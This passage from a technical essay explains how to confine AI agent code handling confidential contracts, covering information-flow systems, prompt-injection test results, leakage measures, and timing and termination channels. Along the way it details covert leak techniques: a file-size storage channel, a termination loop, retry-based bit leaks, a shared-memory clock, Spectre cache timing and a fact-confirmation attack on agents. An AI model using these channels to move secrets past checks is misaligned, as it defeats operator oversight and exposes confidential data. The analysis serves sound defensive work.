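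Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of secrets, including API keys and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 legitimate tasks with ten prompt injections and added 11 requests for secrets, some from a supposed administrator. Two models attempted all 131 trials, once with the secrets wrapped and once with them as ordinary text. A trial passed if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

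| Model | Secrets | Trials without a leak | Legitimate tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Wrapped | 100% | 99.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Ordinary text | 98.5% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Wrapped | 100% | 90.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Ordinary text | 91.6% | 88.3% |

Without the wrapper, Sonnet leaked secrets in two trials and MiniMax in 11, eight of which used direct or deceptive requests. The models leaked nothing in the other 249 unwrapped trials, so the matching wrapped trials provide little evidence about the wrapper. The test looked for secrets in the output but did not check for leaks through timing.

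The wrapper probably did not make Sonnet better at its tasks. Odersky and colleagues suggest that Sonnet often ran out of time or turns in the unwrapped trials and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

They also ran two other models on AgentDojo, where one of 1,926 attacks succeeded. The agent had booked the right hotel, but AgentDojo counted the attack as successful because the agent quoted a review that recommended another hotel. TACIT did worse than CaMeL on office tasks with o4-mini-high, completing 52.9% to CaMeL's 81.4%, but better on travel tasks with Gemini 2.5 Pro, completing 64.3% to CaMeL's 1.4%. According to the agent's instructions for these tests, side effects inside `map` happen immediately. This suggests that some functions inside the wrapper could have side effects, so the result may not be a test of strict purity.

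Models did about as well writing Scala as they did making ordinary tool calls. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for an airline and a shop, three models solved between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points more tasks with Scala. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems, MiniMax solved 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% without, a difference of five problems. At most 7.9% of the Scala programs on τ²-bench needed a retry, usually one or two, and checking a program took less than a second. The τ²-bench tools returned ordinary data, so these figures don't measure the effect of keeping data wrapped, only that of using Scala.

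### What a passing check leaves open

If the trusted parts are correct, a passing check means that the program's own code cannot copy wrapped text to an ordinary output. The check does not test whether a summary is accurate, and it covers only text that TACIT has wrapped. A contract saved outside the protected folders is not wrapped, so the program can handle it as ordinary text.

Odersky and colleagues do not cover leaks through timing and termination. A function inside `map` can run for longer if a contract mentions a penalty, and the agent's model can detect the delay. They describe this as leaking a single bit, but a program could repeat it, testing for a different fact each time. The type check does not limit how many bits leak this way, so the operator needs a separate timing defence.

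They also exclude external commands, which run outside the language. A program allowed to run `cat`, a command that prints files, could get a protected contract back as ordinary text. TACIT has a strict mode that blocks such file commands, but it is off by default. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific safe commands and adding a sandbox.

TACIT's own library could open a storage channel. Its interface lets a program write wrapped text to a protected file and includes an ordinary method that returns a file's size. Unless the library blocks that method for protected files, a program could use `map` to turn one letter of a contract into text of a corresponding length, write that text to a protected file and read the file's size. The program could recover the whole contract by repeating this for each letter, even though every function passed to `map` would be pure.

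### Purity in Joe-E

Capability languages could express pure functions long before TACIT. Joe-E, a subset of Java that Adrian Mettler, David Wagner and Tyler Close described in 2010, had no global mutable state and allowed access to files and the network only through capabilities. If all of a method's arguments were immutable, including the object it was called on, the method could not change anything or read anything that changed. Anyone could therefore tell from the method's signature that it was pure.

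Such a method was also deterministic, meaning that the same arguments always gave the same result. Joe-E prevented programs from catching errors such as running out of memory, since those depend on the state of the machine. TACIT's pure functions need not be deterministic, because `chat` can give different answers to the same question. That does not release any secrets, but an auditor cannot check a summary by running the program again.

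Joe-E's verifier checked code before it ran, so Odersky and colleagues overstate when they write that languages like Joe-E rely only on run-time mechanisms. They argue more convincingly that, to get local purity, Joe-E's designers would have to track capabilities in types or forbid closures, which are functions that carry references with them, from holding any capabilities. A capture set lets a closure hold references and records which ones it holds.

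### The contracts program in Scala

To use this approach, the operator can give the contracts program a folder that returns wrapped documents, a summary file that accepts wrapped text, and a status object that accepts only ordinary text. The core of the program is then short:

```scala
for (name, i) <- folder.list().zipWithIndex do
  val contract = folder.read(name)
  val section = chat(contract.map(text => s"Summarise this contract:\n$text"))
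  summary.append(section)
  status.post(s"${i + 1} contracts finished")
```

The function inside `map` adds an instruction to the contract's text, and `chat` passes both to the second model. The resulting section is still wrapped when the program adds it to the summary file. The status message depends only on the loop counter, so the program can report progress, as it could with labels. File names are ordinary text here, so the operator should replace any that reveal information about a contract.

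The compiler rejects `status.post(section)` because the section is not ordinary text. It also rejects `section.map(s => status.post(s))` because the function captures `status`. If the program puts the section inside a longer message, the code compiles, but readers see only `Classified(****)` in place of the section.

Changing `flagged` inside `map` is a compile error, so the program never starts and this mistake no longer leaks anything. The agent can instead write `section.map(_.contains("penalty"))`, which produces a wrapped true or false for the summary.

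The wrapper is less flexible than labels in other ways. It does not record that the sales team may read the Acme contract and the finance team may read the Birch contract, so the operator would need a separate wrapper or a separate run for each team. The program also cannot email Acme about an unusual clause, because it cannot unwrap the clause. The operator could add a trusted function that unwraps text and sends it to Acme's address, but the compiler would not limit how much of the contract the agent put in the email.

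## Allowing limited disclosure and counting the bits

Some tasks require a program to tell outsiders something derived from a contract. The operator must then make exceptions to the labels or type checks and decide what each exception may reveal and how often the program may use it.

### Declassification and endorsement

Declassification relaxes a value's secrecy label so that more people may read it. The contracts program would need it to tell an outsider that a contract is up for renewal. Endorsement, the matching operation for trust labels, marks an untrusted value as trusted. The program would need it to let a date in a supplier's contract decide when a payment goes out.

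Someone or something must have the authority to make these exceptions. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) describes a monitor that can refer a forbidden tool call to an outside authority, which may be a fixed rule, a human reviewer or another model. The operator declares in advance what each authority may approve, and the agent's own model can't approve anything. An approval covers the exact text of one call and changes no labels, so the agent needs a new approval for the next call.

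FIDES can instead let trusted decisions override the secrecy rule. Costa and colleagues describe this as a form of robust declassification, because an attacker who plants text in a document cannot trigger the release. They assume that a release decided in a trusted context is intentional. This assumption is generous for agent code because a model can make a mistake without an attacker's influence.

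A policy can also specify which information a program may release. Birgisson and Sabelfeld, in *Multi-run security*, use "escape hatches", expressions whose values a program may reveal. If `h` is a secret number, the escape hatch `h % 4` lets the program reveal the remainder after division by four and nothing else about `h`. A program could get around this limit by copying a different secret into `h` first, so their type checker forbids assignments to any variable in an escape hatch.

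Free text has no such simple expression, so FlowSeal uses a separate model to check whether a proposed output reveals a protected record. Shim and colleagues show that a leak need not contain any secret text. In one of their attacks, an outsider gives the agent a list of true and invented facts about a person and asks it to delete the wrong ones. The true entries remain, so a list of 20 can reveal up to 20 bits. FlowSeal's checker sees both the protected records and the proposed edit. In a test with live Gmail and Notion accounts, FlowSeal reduced leakage from this attack to 0%, compared with 34.7% under a defence that relied on the agent's model to recognise privacy violations.

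### Keeping a release in one dimension

LLMbda splits each label into a trust part and a secrecy part so that endorsing a secret doesn't make it public. When a program endorses a value, the result takes its trust part from the label the program requested and its secrecy part from the original value. The runtime then joins this label with the program-counter label. If a program endorses a secret password as trusted and public, the password becomes trusted but stays secret.

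The program-counter label also stops untrusted code from endorsing its own data. If the program runs code built from a supplier's text, everything that code endorses remains untrusted. Garby and colleagues prove their secrecy theorem for any division of labels into two independent parts, so swapping the parts gives a declassification operation that cannot make untrusted data trusted.

A chain of endorsements can still get around the program-counter label. If a program endorses a supplier's text by mistake and then runs it as code, that code counts as trusted and can endorse other values. Garby and colleagues suggest a wrapper that marks every endorsed value and refuses to endorse a marked value again.

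Another of their wrappers endorses a value only if it appears on a fixed list of *n* values, which limits the attacker's influence to log₂ *n* bits per endorsement. They leave a formal proof of that bound to future work. The wrapper works for categories but not for account numbers, so it would reject the endorsements their banking agent needs most.

### Measuring a leak

Let *X* be the secret and *Y* everything an outsider can observe. The older measure of leakage uses Shannon entropy, the average uncertainty about a value in bits:

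*H(X)* = −Σ *p(x)* log₂ *p(x)*

*H(X|Y)* is the average uncertainty that remains after the outsider has seen *Y*, and the Shannon leakage is *H(X)* − *H(X|Y)*.

Min-entropy leakage uses the chance of guessing the secret in one try. Before seeing any output, the outsider should guess the most likely value, and afterwards the most likely value given that output. The chances of success are

*V(X)* = max *p(x)* and *V(X|Y)* = Σ *p(y)* max *p(x|y)*,

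where each maximum is over *x* and the sum is over *y*. The leakage is log₂(*V(X|Y)* / *V(X)*), so each bit doubles the chance of a correct guess.

*On Bounding Problems of Quantitative Information Flow* (2011) analyzes two programs with a secret that has four equally likely values. By Shannon's measure, the program that reveals only whether the secret equals one particular value leaks 0.81 bits, and the program that reveals the whole secret leaks 2 bits. *Quantitative Information Flow* (2010) uses min-entropy and calculates leaks of 1 bit and 2 bits for its own two examples. The 1-bit leak raises an outsider's chance of guessing the secret correctly from 1/4 to 1/2.

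The two measures can differ much more than this. Smith (2009), in *On the Foundations of Quantitative Information Flow*, argued that Shannon leakage gives poor guarantees against an attacker who has one guess at the secret. Suppose a contract contains a random 64-bit key. Program A publishes the whole key if its last three bits are zero, and otherwise publishes "no". Program B always publishes the last nine bits.

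| | Program A | Program B |
|---|---|---|
| Shannon leakage | 8.2 bits | 9 bits |
| Chance of guessing the key afterwards | About 1 in 8 | 1 in 2⁵⁵ |
| Min-entropy leakage | 61 bits | 9 bits |

Program A looks slightly safer by Shannon's measure because that measure averages over all keys, and the program reveals almost nothing about seven in eight of them, though the outsider learns the rest completely. *Quantifying Information Leakage in Finite Order Deterministic Programs* (2010) also reports pairs of programs that different entropy measures rank in opposite orders.

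An operator rarely knows the probabilities in these formulas, but can often count the possible outputs. If an outsider can distinguish at most *k* outcomes, the program leaks at most log₂ *k* bits by either measure. For min-entropy, the proof takes two steps:

1. For each output *y*, the term *p(y)* max *p(x|y)* equals the largest joint probability *p(x, y)*. This cannot exceed *V(X)*, because *p(x, y)* ≤ *p(x)*.
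2. There are at most *k* such terms, so *V(X|Y)* ≤ *k* · *V(X)*. Dividing by *V(X)* and taking the logarithm gives log₂ *k*.

With *k* distinguishable outcomes, Shannon leakage is at most log₂ *k* bits because it cannot exceed the entropy of the output. The min-entropy leakage is exactly log₂ *k* bits if the program is deterministic, all secrets are equally likely and all *k* outcomes can occur. The upper bound also holds for random programs, which matters when agent code calls a language model. Applying the bound doesn't require reading the code, but *k* must include everything that outsiders can tell apart, such as error messages, silence and the order of messages.

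### Small outputs add up

A program that chooses one of eight categories reveals up to log₂ 8 = 3 bits. If it makes 1,000 such choices, there are 8¹⁰⁰⁰ possible sequences, so it can reveal up to 3,000 bits, enough to encode 500 characters from a 64-character alphabet.

Lampson estimated that a bill in a suitably restricted form could still carry "a few bits or tens of bits". The formula gives a consistent figure of up to about 10 bits if the conversion company charges for between 1 and 1,000 pages. A single category carries less information than that bill, but 1,000 categories can carry 300 times as much as the bill.

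FIDES can optionally relax its rules for values that carry little information. When its separate model answers in a fixed format, such as true or false, FIDES adds the type to the answer's label. It orders types by how much information they can carry, from Booleans through fixed lists of options to free text. A policy can then let an untrusted Boolean influence an important action because the attacker controls only one bit, or release a secret Boolean because it reveals only one bit.

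This argument works for one Boolean at a time. Joining a label with itself changes nothing, so an agent that has read 1,000 secret Booleans has the same label as an agent that has read one. The type limits the size of each answer but not the number of answers, so a separate mechanism has to count them. Garby and colleagues add that an auditor can't tell from a single run whether a value admitted this way was a harmless release or a leak. They also note that FIDES's evaluation did not use the allowance.

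APPA applies a similar restriction to whole tasks. When an agent needs to read untrusted or confidential data, it can start a temporary copy of its conversation, called a child branch. Before the child reads anything, the parent sets the form of the answer. The form may contain Booleans, whole numbers within a range, decimals of fixed precision, options from a closed list, and lists or records of limited size, but not free text. APPA checks the answer against the form and discards the child's conversation.

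For the contracts program, the form might ask for one of four risk levels, a count of unusual clauses from 0 to 15, and one of ten renewal years. There are 4 × 16 × 10 = 640 possible answers, so each answer carries at most about 9.3 bits. Forms with lists need more care. Even a limited list of 100 numbers from 0 to 255 can carry 800 bits, enough for 100 characters of contract text.

The check confirms only that the answer has the right form. A child that has read a malicious document can still choose a false answer from the permitted ones. Kravchenko and colleagues write that validation "declassifies nothing", because information can leak slowly even through choices from a closed list. The operator has to separately authorise giving the answer a less restrictive label than the child's.

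Child branches help agents finish their work. On a benchmark of office tasks, an agent using APPA with GPT-5.6 Luna completed 88% of its attempts, but only 56.5% when Kravchenko and colleagues removed the branches. No attack succeeded in 1,320 test runs with APPA's protections on. These tests counted successful attacks, so they don't measure how much an agent could leak through a series of valid answers.

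### The termination channel

Many information-flow systems tolerate leaks through the termination channel (whether a run finishes, fails or is blocked) on the grounds that one run reveals at most one bit. Askarov, Hunt and colleagues, in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit*, showed that this is wrong if a program can send messages before it stops. Their example works like this:

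```python
for i in range(limit):
    send(i)
    if i == secret:
        while True:
            pass
```

Each message contains only the public counter, so several checking tools accept the program, but the last number to arrive is the secret. If an outsider watches for up to *t* messages, there are *t* + 1 possible outcomes, so the program can leak log₂(*t* + 1) bits. The mistake with `flagged` in the labelled contracts program leaked nearly seven bits in this way.

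This attack is slow for large secrets because it tests one value per message. Askarov and colleagues recovered a 32-bit number in under six seconds, but estimated 18½ days for a credit card number of about 50 bits. A random 128-bit key would take far too long to recover. They proved that no program satisfying termination-insensitive noninterference can reliably leak a secret in a single run much faster than by trying every value.

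Repeated runs remove that protection. Birgisson and Sabelfeld describe a program that loops forever if a chosen bit of the secret is 1 and finishes if it is 0. An attacker who can rerun the program, choosing a different bit each time, needs only one run per bit. Using a program that had passed the checks of Jif, a secure version of Java, the two researchers leaked about one bit per second and estimated that leaking a credit card number would take less than a minute.

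CaMeL's retry loop, which starts each attempt without the old labels, makes the same attack possible. Suppose a contract's price is a whole number of dollars below 1,048,576, so it fits in 20 bits. On attempt *i*, the program fails if bit *i* of the price is 1. Each attempt leaks one bit, which the label system tolerates. If the loop runs for 20 attempts, an outsider who sees which ones fail learns the exact price.

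The bound depends on what outsiders can see. If they see whether each of 20 attempts succeeds or fails, there are 2²⁰ possible sequences, so the attempts can reveal up to 20 bits. If the loop stops at the first success and outsiders see only which attempt succeeded, if any, there are 21 possible outcomes, and the bound is log₂ 21, or about 4.4 bits. The 4.4-bit bound no longer holds if outsiders can also see error messages, or if the agent starts a new loop after each success.

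Birgisson and Sabelfeld prevent the attack with a type rule that forbids any loop condition that depends on both secret data and data the attacker controls. A program that follows this rule leaks at most one bit through termination, however many times the attacker runs it, as long as the secret stays the same. But their theorem covers only one fixed program. An agent usually rewrites its code after a failure, and each new version could leak a different bit, so the agent's operator still has to limit and count the attempts.

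### When a small output is not safe

An outsider can learn much more from small answers by choosing each question after hearing the previous answer. Suppose the contracts program will tell an outsider whether the price is above any given amount. If the outsider must choose 20 amounts in advance, the answers divide the possible prices into 21 ranges and reveal at most 4.4 bits. But 20 answers can identify the exact price among a million possibilities if the outsider chooses each amount to halve the remaining range. Every answer is a single Boolean in both cases, so checking the form of the answers would not distinguish them.

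Refusals can also leak information. FlowSeal's checker returns only "safe" or "blocked", because an explanation might reveal something about the protected records. But if an outsider can propose a message and see whether FlowSeal blocks it, each attempt may still confirm or rule out a guess. Refusals that outsiders can see therefore have to count towards the total.

Small outputs are also unsafe when the secret has few possible values. If three companies bid for a contract, the winner's identity contains at most 1.6 bits, and an output of a single category can reveal it completely. The results of Askarov and colleagues on guessing are for large, random secrets, so they don't apply here.

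Measured leakage can look even smaller when one answer was already likely. Suppose that outsiders think there is a 10% chance that a company is about to be sold, and the program reveals whether it is. Their chance of guessing correctly rises from 90% to 100%, a min-entropy leakage of only 0.15 bits. Yet if the company is being sold, the outsiders have gone from thinking a sale unlikely to knowing about it. The operator should therefore keep such a fact out of the data the program uses to compute its releases.

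### A lifetime limit for the contracts program

Suppose the operator wants outsiders to see one of eight categories for each of the 120 contracts, which discloses 120 × 3 = 360 bits. The program has up to 20 attempts to produce the list, and outsiders can see how many it needed. This adds about 4.3 bits, since there are 20 possible counts. The operator rounds the total up to 365 bits and sets a lifetime limit of 400 bits for the folder.

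The operator gives the program an object with one method instead of the ordinary status object:

```js
function makePublisher(ledger, status, categories, count) {
  return harden({
    publish(choices) {
      const lines = [];
      for (let i = 0; i < count; i += 1) {
        const choice = choices[i];
        const safe = categories.includes(choice) ? choice : 'other';
        lines.push(`Contract ${i + 1}: ${safe}`);
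      }
      ledger.spend(365);
      status.post(lines.join('\n'));
    },
  });
}
```

The list `categories` holds eight fixed strings, including "other". The ledger is a counter that belongs to the operator. Its `spend` method saves the new total before returning, and throws an error if the total would exceed the limit. The method always adds the full amount to the total, even if every contract falls into the same category. If the amount varied with the program's choices, anyone who could see the remaining balance could learn something about the contracts.

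The fixed order of the lines matters as much as the fixed categories. If the program could report the contracts in any order, its choice among the 120! possible orders could carry another 660 bits.

A second run would exceed the limit, so the ledger would block it. If someone only needs to see the results again, the operator's code can save the published list and repost it without counting more bits against the limit, because repeating it reveals nothing new. Running the program again does count, because a new version of the code could encode different information in the same categories.

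The limit holds only if several things outlast the run:

- The total must belong to the contracts. If it belonged to the program, the sandbox or the conversation, a restart or a rewritten program would begin again at zero. A copy of the folder has to share the same total, and restoring a backup must not lower it.
- Every output to outsiders that depends on the contracts must draw on that total, including any that the operator adds later. Separate limits for separate outsiders would fail if they compared notes.
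- The ledger must handle one charge at a time, so that two tasks running in parallel cannot both spend the last 365 bits.
- The record must last as long as the contracts remain confidential, because nobody can take back what outsiders have learned.

The ledger is compatible with Lampson's rule that a confined program keeps no memory between calls, as long as only the operator's code can write to the ledger.

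APPA already has a log that all branches of a task share, and Kravchenko and colleagues mention using it to track spending. A disclosure counter would need different rules, because APPA's log counts only effects that a tool reports as successful. A message may reach outsiders even if the status service then returns an error, so the counter has to go up before each post and stay up even if the post fails.

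This kind of limit doesn't help much with an email to Acme about an unusual clause, because a few sentences of free text would use up all 400 bits. The operator has to rely instead on labels that restrict the email to information from Acme's own contract, or on a person who approves its exact text. The 365 bits also don't include information revealed by when the list of categories appears, which can depend on the contracts.

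## Closing or narrowing timing channels

The right defence against a timing leak depends on whether the observer is inside or outside the runtime. Another program inside the runtime has only the clocks that the operator gives it, so the operator can remove them. The operator can't remove an outside observer's clock, and so has to control when outputs appear.

### Programs without clocks

Suppose the contracts program shares a runtime with a formatter, a small program that lays out text. The contracts program tries to send the formatter a bit by running a calculation for 1 millisecond to signal a 0 or 100 milliseconds to signal a 1. The formatter starts later for a 1, but each of its instructions gives the same result either way, so it can't read the bit.

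This defence doesn't require anyone to find the leak first. Miller explains that it suits JavaScript because the language almost completely separates pure computation from the objects that reach the outside world. The exceptions are the current time and random numbers, and Hardened JavaScript disables both. It disables random numbers because one program could otherwise detect that another had drawn from the shared generator. A program can still identify the engine it is running on, but the engine doesn't change during a run, so it can't carry a signal.

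The operator must also avoid stopping the formatter after a fixed number of seconds, because whether it finished would then depend on how busy the machine was, which the contracts program can influence.

Lipner's *A Comment on the Confinement Problem* (1975) had already suggested a scheme of this kind. According to Purdue's *Information Flow, Confinement & Covert Channels*, each program would see a virtual time that depended only on its own activity. Lipner doubted this could work, because users also have a sense of time outside the system.

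Later researchers built systems around virtual time, and *Time Protection* (Ge, Chothia and colleagues, 2018) mentions two of them. Determinator gives programs in a data centre only virtual time. StopWatch runs three copies of a system and releases each visible event at the median of the copies' times, which makes the system much slower.

### How a program gets a clock back

A program can build a clock from anything that changes at a fairly steady rate while it runs:

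- With network access, it can ask a server for the time, or use the arrival of replies as ticks.
- With shared memory, it can have a second thread count continuously and read the count before and after an operation.
- With concurrency, it can start two tasks and see which finishes first. The order shows which was slower, although no number ever appears.

The shared-memory clock takes only a few lines:

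```js
// Second thread
while (true) Atomics.add(ticks, 0, 1);

// Main thread
const start = Atomics.load(ticks, 0);
operation();
const elapsed = Atomics.load(ticks, 0) - start;
```

Miller accepts that most applications need users or networks and so can't practically avoid timing channels. Ge and colleagues call removing real time infeasible except in extremely constrained cases. A formatter or parser is such a case, since it can receive all its input at the start, return an answer and stop. The contracts program would get a clock from the conversion service's replies, so it doesn't qualify.

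Splitting the program only partly solves this. The reading program has no network access, but the reporting program could send it a message every second through the one-way channel, which would give it a clock. To prevent this, the operator has to deliver all of the reading program's input before that program starts.

Making a clock coarser is a weaker measure than removing it. Vasilikos, Nielson and colleagues, in *Timing Leaks and Coarse-Grained Clocks*, model a clock with grain *g* as showing ⌊*t*/*g*⌋ · *g* at time *t*. They prove that a coarser clock can leak more than a finer one. For example, a clock that advances every 4 milliseconds reads 4 after both 5 and 6 milliseconds. A clock that advances every 6 milliseconds reads 0 after 5 milliseconds and 6 after 6, so a program that reads it can distinguish the two times.

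Making a clock coarser can't reveal new timing differences in a deterministic system if the new grain is a multiple of the old one, because any two times that looked the same before still do. But a program can recover the lost precision by counting loop iterations from the end of an operation until the clock next advances. The count shows how far through the clock interval the operation finished. Coarse clocks therefore make attacks slower and noisier but don't rule them out.

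### Secrets in the same process

Spectre showed that a program with a clock can read secrets from objects that were not written to send them. Processors predict which instructions come next and run them early. If a prediction is wrong, the processor discards the results, but the data those instructions loaded stays in its cache, a small store of recently used data. An attacking program causes a wrong prediction that makes the processor read a secret and use it to choose which memory location to load. The program then times its own memory accesses. The location that was already cached loads faster, which reveals the secret.

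Object capabilities don't prevent a timing attack from exposing a secret, because the attack needs no reference to the secret. The attack can expose the status service's key even when the key is in the status object's private state, so the operator should run that object in a different process from agent code that has a clock.

V8's *Untrusted code mitigations*, guidance for companies that build Google's JavaScript engine into their products, recommends keeping untrusted code in a separate process from any sensitive data. A Spectre attack of this type can then read only data in the attacker's own process. The guidance also recommends making precise timers coarser or adding random variation to them.

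In 2018, V8 added protections against Spectre that limit the memory that speculatively executed instructions can reach. They barely slow a typical web benchmark but can slow heavy computation by up to 15%. They are off by default on platforms where process isolation is expected, so an operator who runs several programs in one process should check that they are on.

Hardened JavaScript's documentation allows a host to give timers to one party per process, provided the process holds no confidential information. A host can easily break this rule by accident. It might give a program a timer for retrying failed requests while a cache in the same process still holds another client's contracts.

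### Time protection in seL4

Programs in different processes still share hardware. When one program fills part of a cache, it displaces another program's data, and the second program has to wait for main memory. Ge and colleagues built a defence called time protection into seL4, a small kernel with machine-checked proofs of its access controls. Time protection applies to all programs, including those that don't cooperate, which is essential when the program itself is leaking information.

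Time protection divides programs into security domains. It gives each domain its own share of the hardware where it can, and resets the rest whenever the processor switches domains.

The kernel divides the large caches by "colouring". The address of each page of memory determines which part of the cache can hold it, so the kernel can give each domain pages that use a different part of the cache. With pages of size *P*, a cache of size *S* with *w* places for each address has *S*/(*wP*) of these parts, called colours. The Arm processor in the tests had a 1 MiB cache with 16 places for each address and 4 KiB pages, so it had 16 colours.

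The kernel also needs to be divided between domains. In one test, two programs had separate cache colours but used the same kernel. The sender signalled by making one of three system calls or none, and the receiver measured which kernel code had stayed in the cache. This channel carried 395 bits per second. Giving each domain its own copy of the kernel made the leak negligible.

Small caches and branch predictors inside each processor core are usually impossible to divide, so the kernel clears them. A switch between domains goes roughly as follows:

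1. The kernel blocks interrupts that belong to the old domain, so that they can't disturb the new one.
2. It changes to the new domain's copy of the kernel.
3. It flushes the caches and predictors inside the core.
4. It loads the few kernel data that all domains share, so that their access times don't depend on the old domain.
5. It waits until a fixed time and then starts the new domain.

The final wait is necessary because flushing takes longer when the old domain has changed more data. Without the wait, this difference alone leaked 1.4 bits per observation on the Arm processor. *Can We Prove Time Protection?* (2019) leaves the length of the wait to the system's designer, who must allow for at least the slowest possible flush.

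Ge and colleagues measured each channel by its mutual information, which is the Shannon leakage per observation. The table gives some of their results in thousandths of a bit:

| Shared hardware | No defence | Time protection | Flushing everything |
|---|---|---|---|
| Small data cache, x86 | 4,000 | 0.6 | 0.5 |
| Branch history, x86 | 1,000 | 0.0 | 0.5 |
| Second-level cache, x86 | 2,700 | 50.5 | 2.3 |
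| Second-level cache, Arm | 1,900 | 1.4 | 21 |

The 50.5 on the x86 processor is a real leak, while the 21 on Arm could be measurement noise. Ge and colleagues attribute most of the x86 leak to a feature that fetches data in advance, because turning it off reduced the leak to 6.4. If a receiver made one observation every 20 milliseconds, 50.5 thousandths of a bit per observation would add up to about 2.5 bits per second. That is above the Orange Book's old limit and enough to send a 128-bit key in under a minute.

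The protections added little direct overhead. On x86, a protected switch took 30 microseconds, not counting the added wait, compared with 271 for flushing every cache and less than 1 without any defence. Most programs in a standard benchmark slowed by less than 2% when they had only half the cache colours. The added wait contributed about 0.7% overhead. With all the protections on and a hostile program sharing the core, programs ran between 5.5% slower and 5.8% faster. Some ran faster because the hostile program could no longer push their data out of the cache.

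These percentages don't include a larger loss of performance. To confine a program that leaks deliberately, the system must run only one domain at a time, even on a processor with several cores. Otherwise the domains could signal to each other through their shared connection to memory, which Ge and colleagues thought current hardware probably couldn't divide. In public clouds, they aimed to prevent only accidental leaks, because customers' programs there can communicate with the outside world anyway.

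### Proofs and hardware in 2026

Earlier seL4 proofs rule out storage channels through any state the kernel tracks. *Proving the Absence of Microarchitectural Timing Channels* (Buckley, 2023) describes a way to extend these proofs by including caches and predictors in the formal model. A proof can then treat a timing leak as information stored in one of these components, without reasoning about durations.

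The extension isn't finished. In September 2026, *Where are we with Time Protection?* (Sison, 2026) reported that the proof for seL4's abstract model was in progress and the proof for its C code was still to come. The first approach tracked every memory address the kernel touched and broke existing proofs in more than 685 places. The new approach instead shows that the kernel's references never point outside a fixed set of addresses. According to the seL4 Summit (2026) programme, this removed the main cause of the breakages.

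The hardware has improved faster, at least in research designs. *Systematic Prevention of On-Core Timing Channels by Full Temporal Partitioning* (2022) found that the existing instructions of an open RISC-V processor core weren't enough for an operating system to enforce time protection. *Two interfaces for seL4 kernel verification* (Sison, 2026) reports that Cheshire, a platform based on that core, now has the missing features. The `fence.t` instruction flushes everything inside the core and waits until a set time. The large cache also has partitions of adjustable size, which the kernel can flush separately.

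An operator can't assume that an ordinary processor has any of this. Trustworthy Systems, which develops time protection, states on its *Time Protection* project page that complete protection isn't possible on present hardware. A RISC-V task group is considering `fence.t` for the standard instruction set, but choosing a RISC-V chip is no protection in itself. *Systematic Assessment of Cache Timing Vulnerabilities on RISC-V Processors* (2025) tested three commercial cores and found 65.9% of the vulnerabilities in its test suite on all three.

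Sison's talk also describes a problem with one-way channels like the data diode between Cassie's two calculators. If the sender writes into memory that the receiver can read, the receiver's reads change the cache's contents. The sender can detect this by timing its next access, so the receiver can send information back to the sender. The kernel can prevent this by copying the data between separate areas of memory while it switches domains, but this adds about 19–34% overhead per page. In September, the group was still adding the necessary waiting time to a version that uses Cheshire's new cache.

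Until such systems are available, the simplest way to stop other customers' programs from reading hardware signals is to run the contracts program on a machine that no other customer uses.

### Releasing results at fixed times

None of these defences affects someone who watches the status service from outside. The operator's remaining choice is when to let each output appear.

Suppose every run of the contracts program finishes within 60 seconds. The bound from counting outcomes applies to times just as it does to messages, so *k* distinguishable release times carry at most log₂ *k* bits:

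| When the result can appear | Possible times | Most it can reveal |
|---|---|---|
| Any millisecond | 60,000 | 15.9 bits |
| Any whole second | 60 | 5.9 bits |
| After 1, 2, 4, 8, 16, 32 or 60 seconds | 7 | 2.8 bits |
| Only after 60 seconds | 1 | 0 bits |

If some runs don't finish and outsiders can tell, the last row has two outcomes and can reveal one bit. The operator can avoid this by always publishing something of the same form:

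```js
async function releaseAtDeadline(job, clock, deadline, publisher) {
  await clock.until(deadline);
  const choices = job.finished() ? job.result() : [];
  publisher.publish(choices);
  job.stop();
}
```

Here `job` runs the agent code in another process and returns plain data, so an endless loop can't delay the release. If the job hasn't finished, the publisher receives an empty list and publishes "other" for all 120 contracts. A finished run could have produced the same list, so outsiders can't tell whether the job finished. The list may also mislead them, so the operator should tell the staff privately that the run failed.

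Retries make the deadline more useful. If outsiders could see, to the millisecond, when each of 20 attempts ended, the times alone could carry about 317 bits, nearly as much as the list of categories. If all the attempts take place before one deadline, outsiders don't learn how many there were, and the charge to the ledger falls from 365 bits to 360.

The same rule must apply to everything outsiders can observe. If the program sends a request to the conversion service halfway through the run, the service can see when it did so, which is another reason to convert the whole folder before the program starts. Other customers may also notice when the job ends if the machine gives them the processor immediately. In TACIT, whose guarantee doesn't cover timing, the agent's model is also an outside observer, and the runtime could return each result to it after a fixed delay.

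Adding random delays is a weak defense against timing channels. *Deterministically Deterring Timing Attacks in Deterland* (2015) notes that added noise has controlled timing channels only for particular workloads, and that researchers have built channels that withstand it. An observer who can repeat a measurement can average the noise away. A deliberate sender can use an error-correcting code to get a message through the noise, as Lampson pointed out for channels based on system load.

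### Predictive mitigation

A fixed deadline is hard to choose for a program that sends many messages or runs for an unknown time. *Predictive black-box mitigation of timing channels* (Askarov, Zhang and Myers, 2010) proposes a component that holds back outputs and releases them on a schedule it predicts from public information. The schedule reveals nothing as long as the predictions hold. When a prediction fails, the component switches to a slower schedule, and outsiders learn only the time of the switch.

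A simple version for status messages works like this:

1. The component plans to release one message every second, and stores any that arrive early.
2. If no message is ready at a planned time, the prediction has failed. The component doubles the interval and plans again from that moment.
3. It never shortens the interval.

To bound the leak, let the program run for *T* seconds. The first failure can't happen before second 1, the second before second 3, or the third before second 7. In general, *N* failures take at least 2ᴺ − 1 seconds, so *N* is at most log₂(*T* + 1). Each failure falls on one of *T* whole seconds or doesn't happen at all. There are therefore at most (*T* + 1)ᴺ possible schedules, and the timing reveals at most

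*N* log₂(*T* + 1) ≤ (log₂(*T* + 1))² bits.

At most 11 failures can occur in an hour, which limits the timing leak to about 130 bits. If the program could instead choose every second whether to post a message, its choices could carry 3,600 bits in that hour. The bound doesn't depend on what the program does, so it holds even for hostile agent code. It covers only timing, so the messages' contents still have to be counted in the ledger.

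In *Predictive Mitigation of Timing Channels for Interactive Systems*, Zhang, Askarov and Myers later found a tighter bound for services that answer requests and tested the method on a web proxy.

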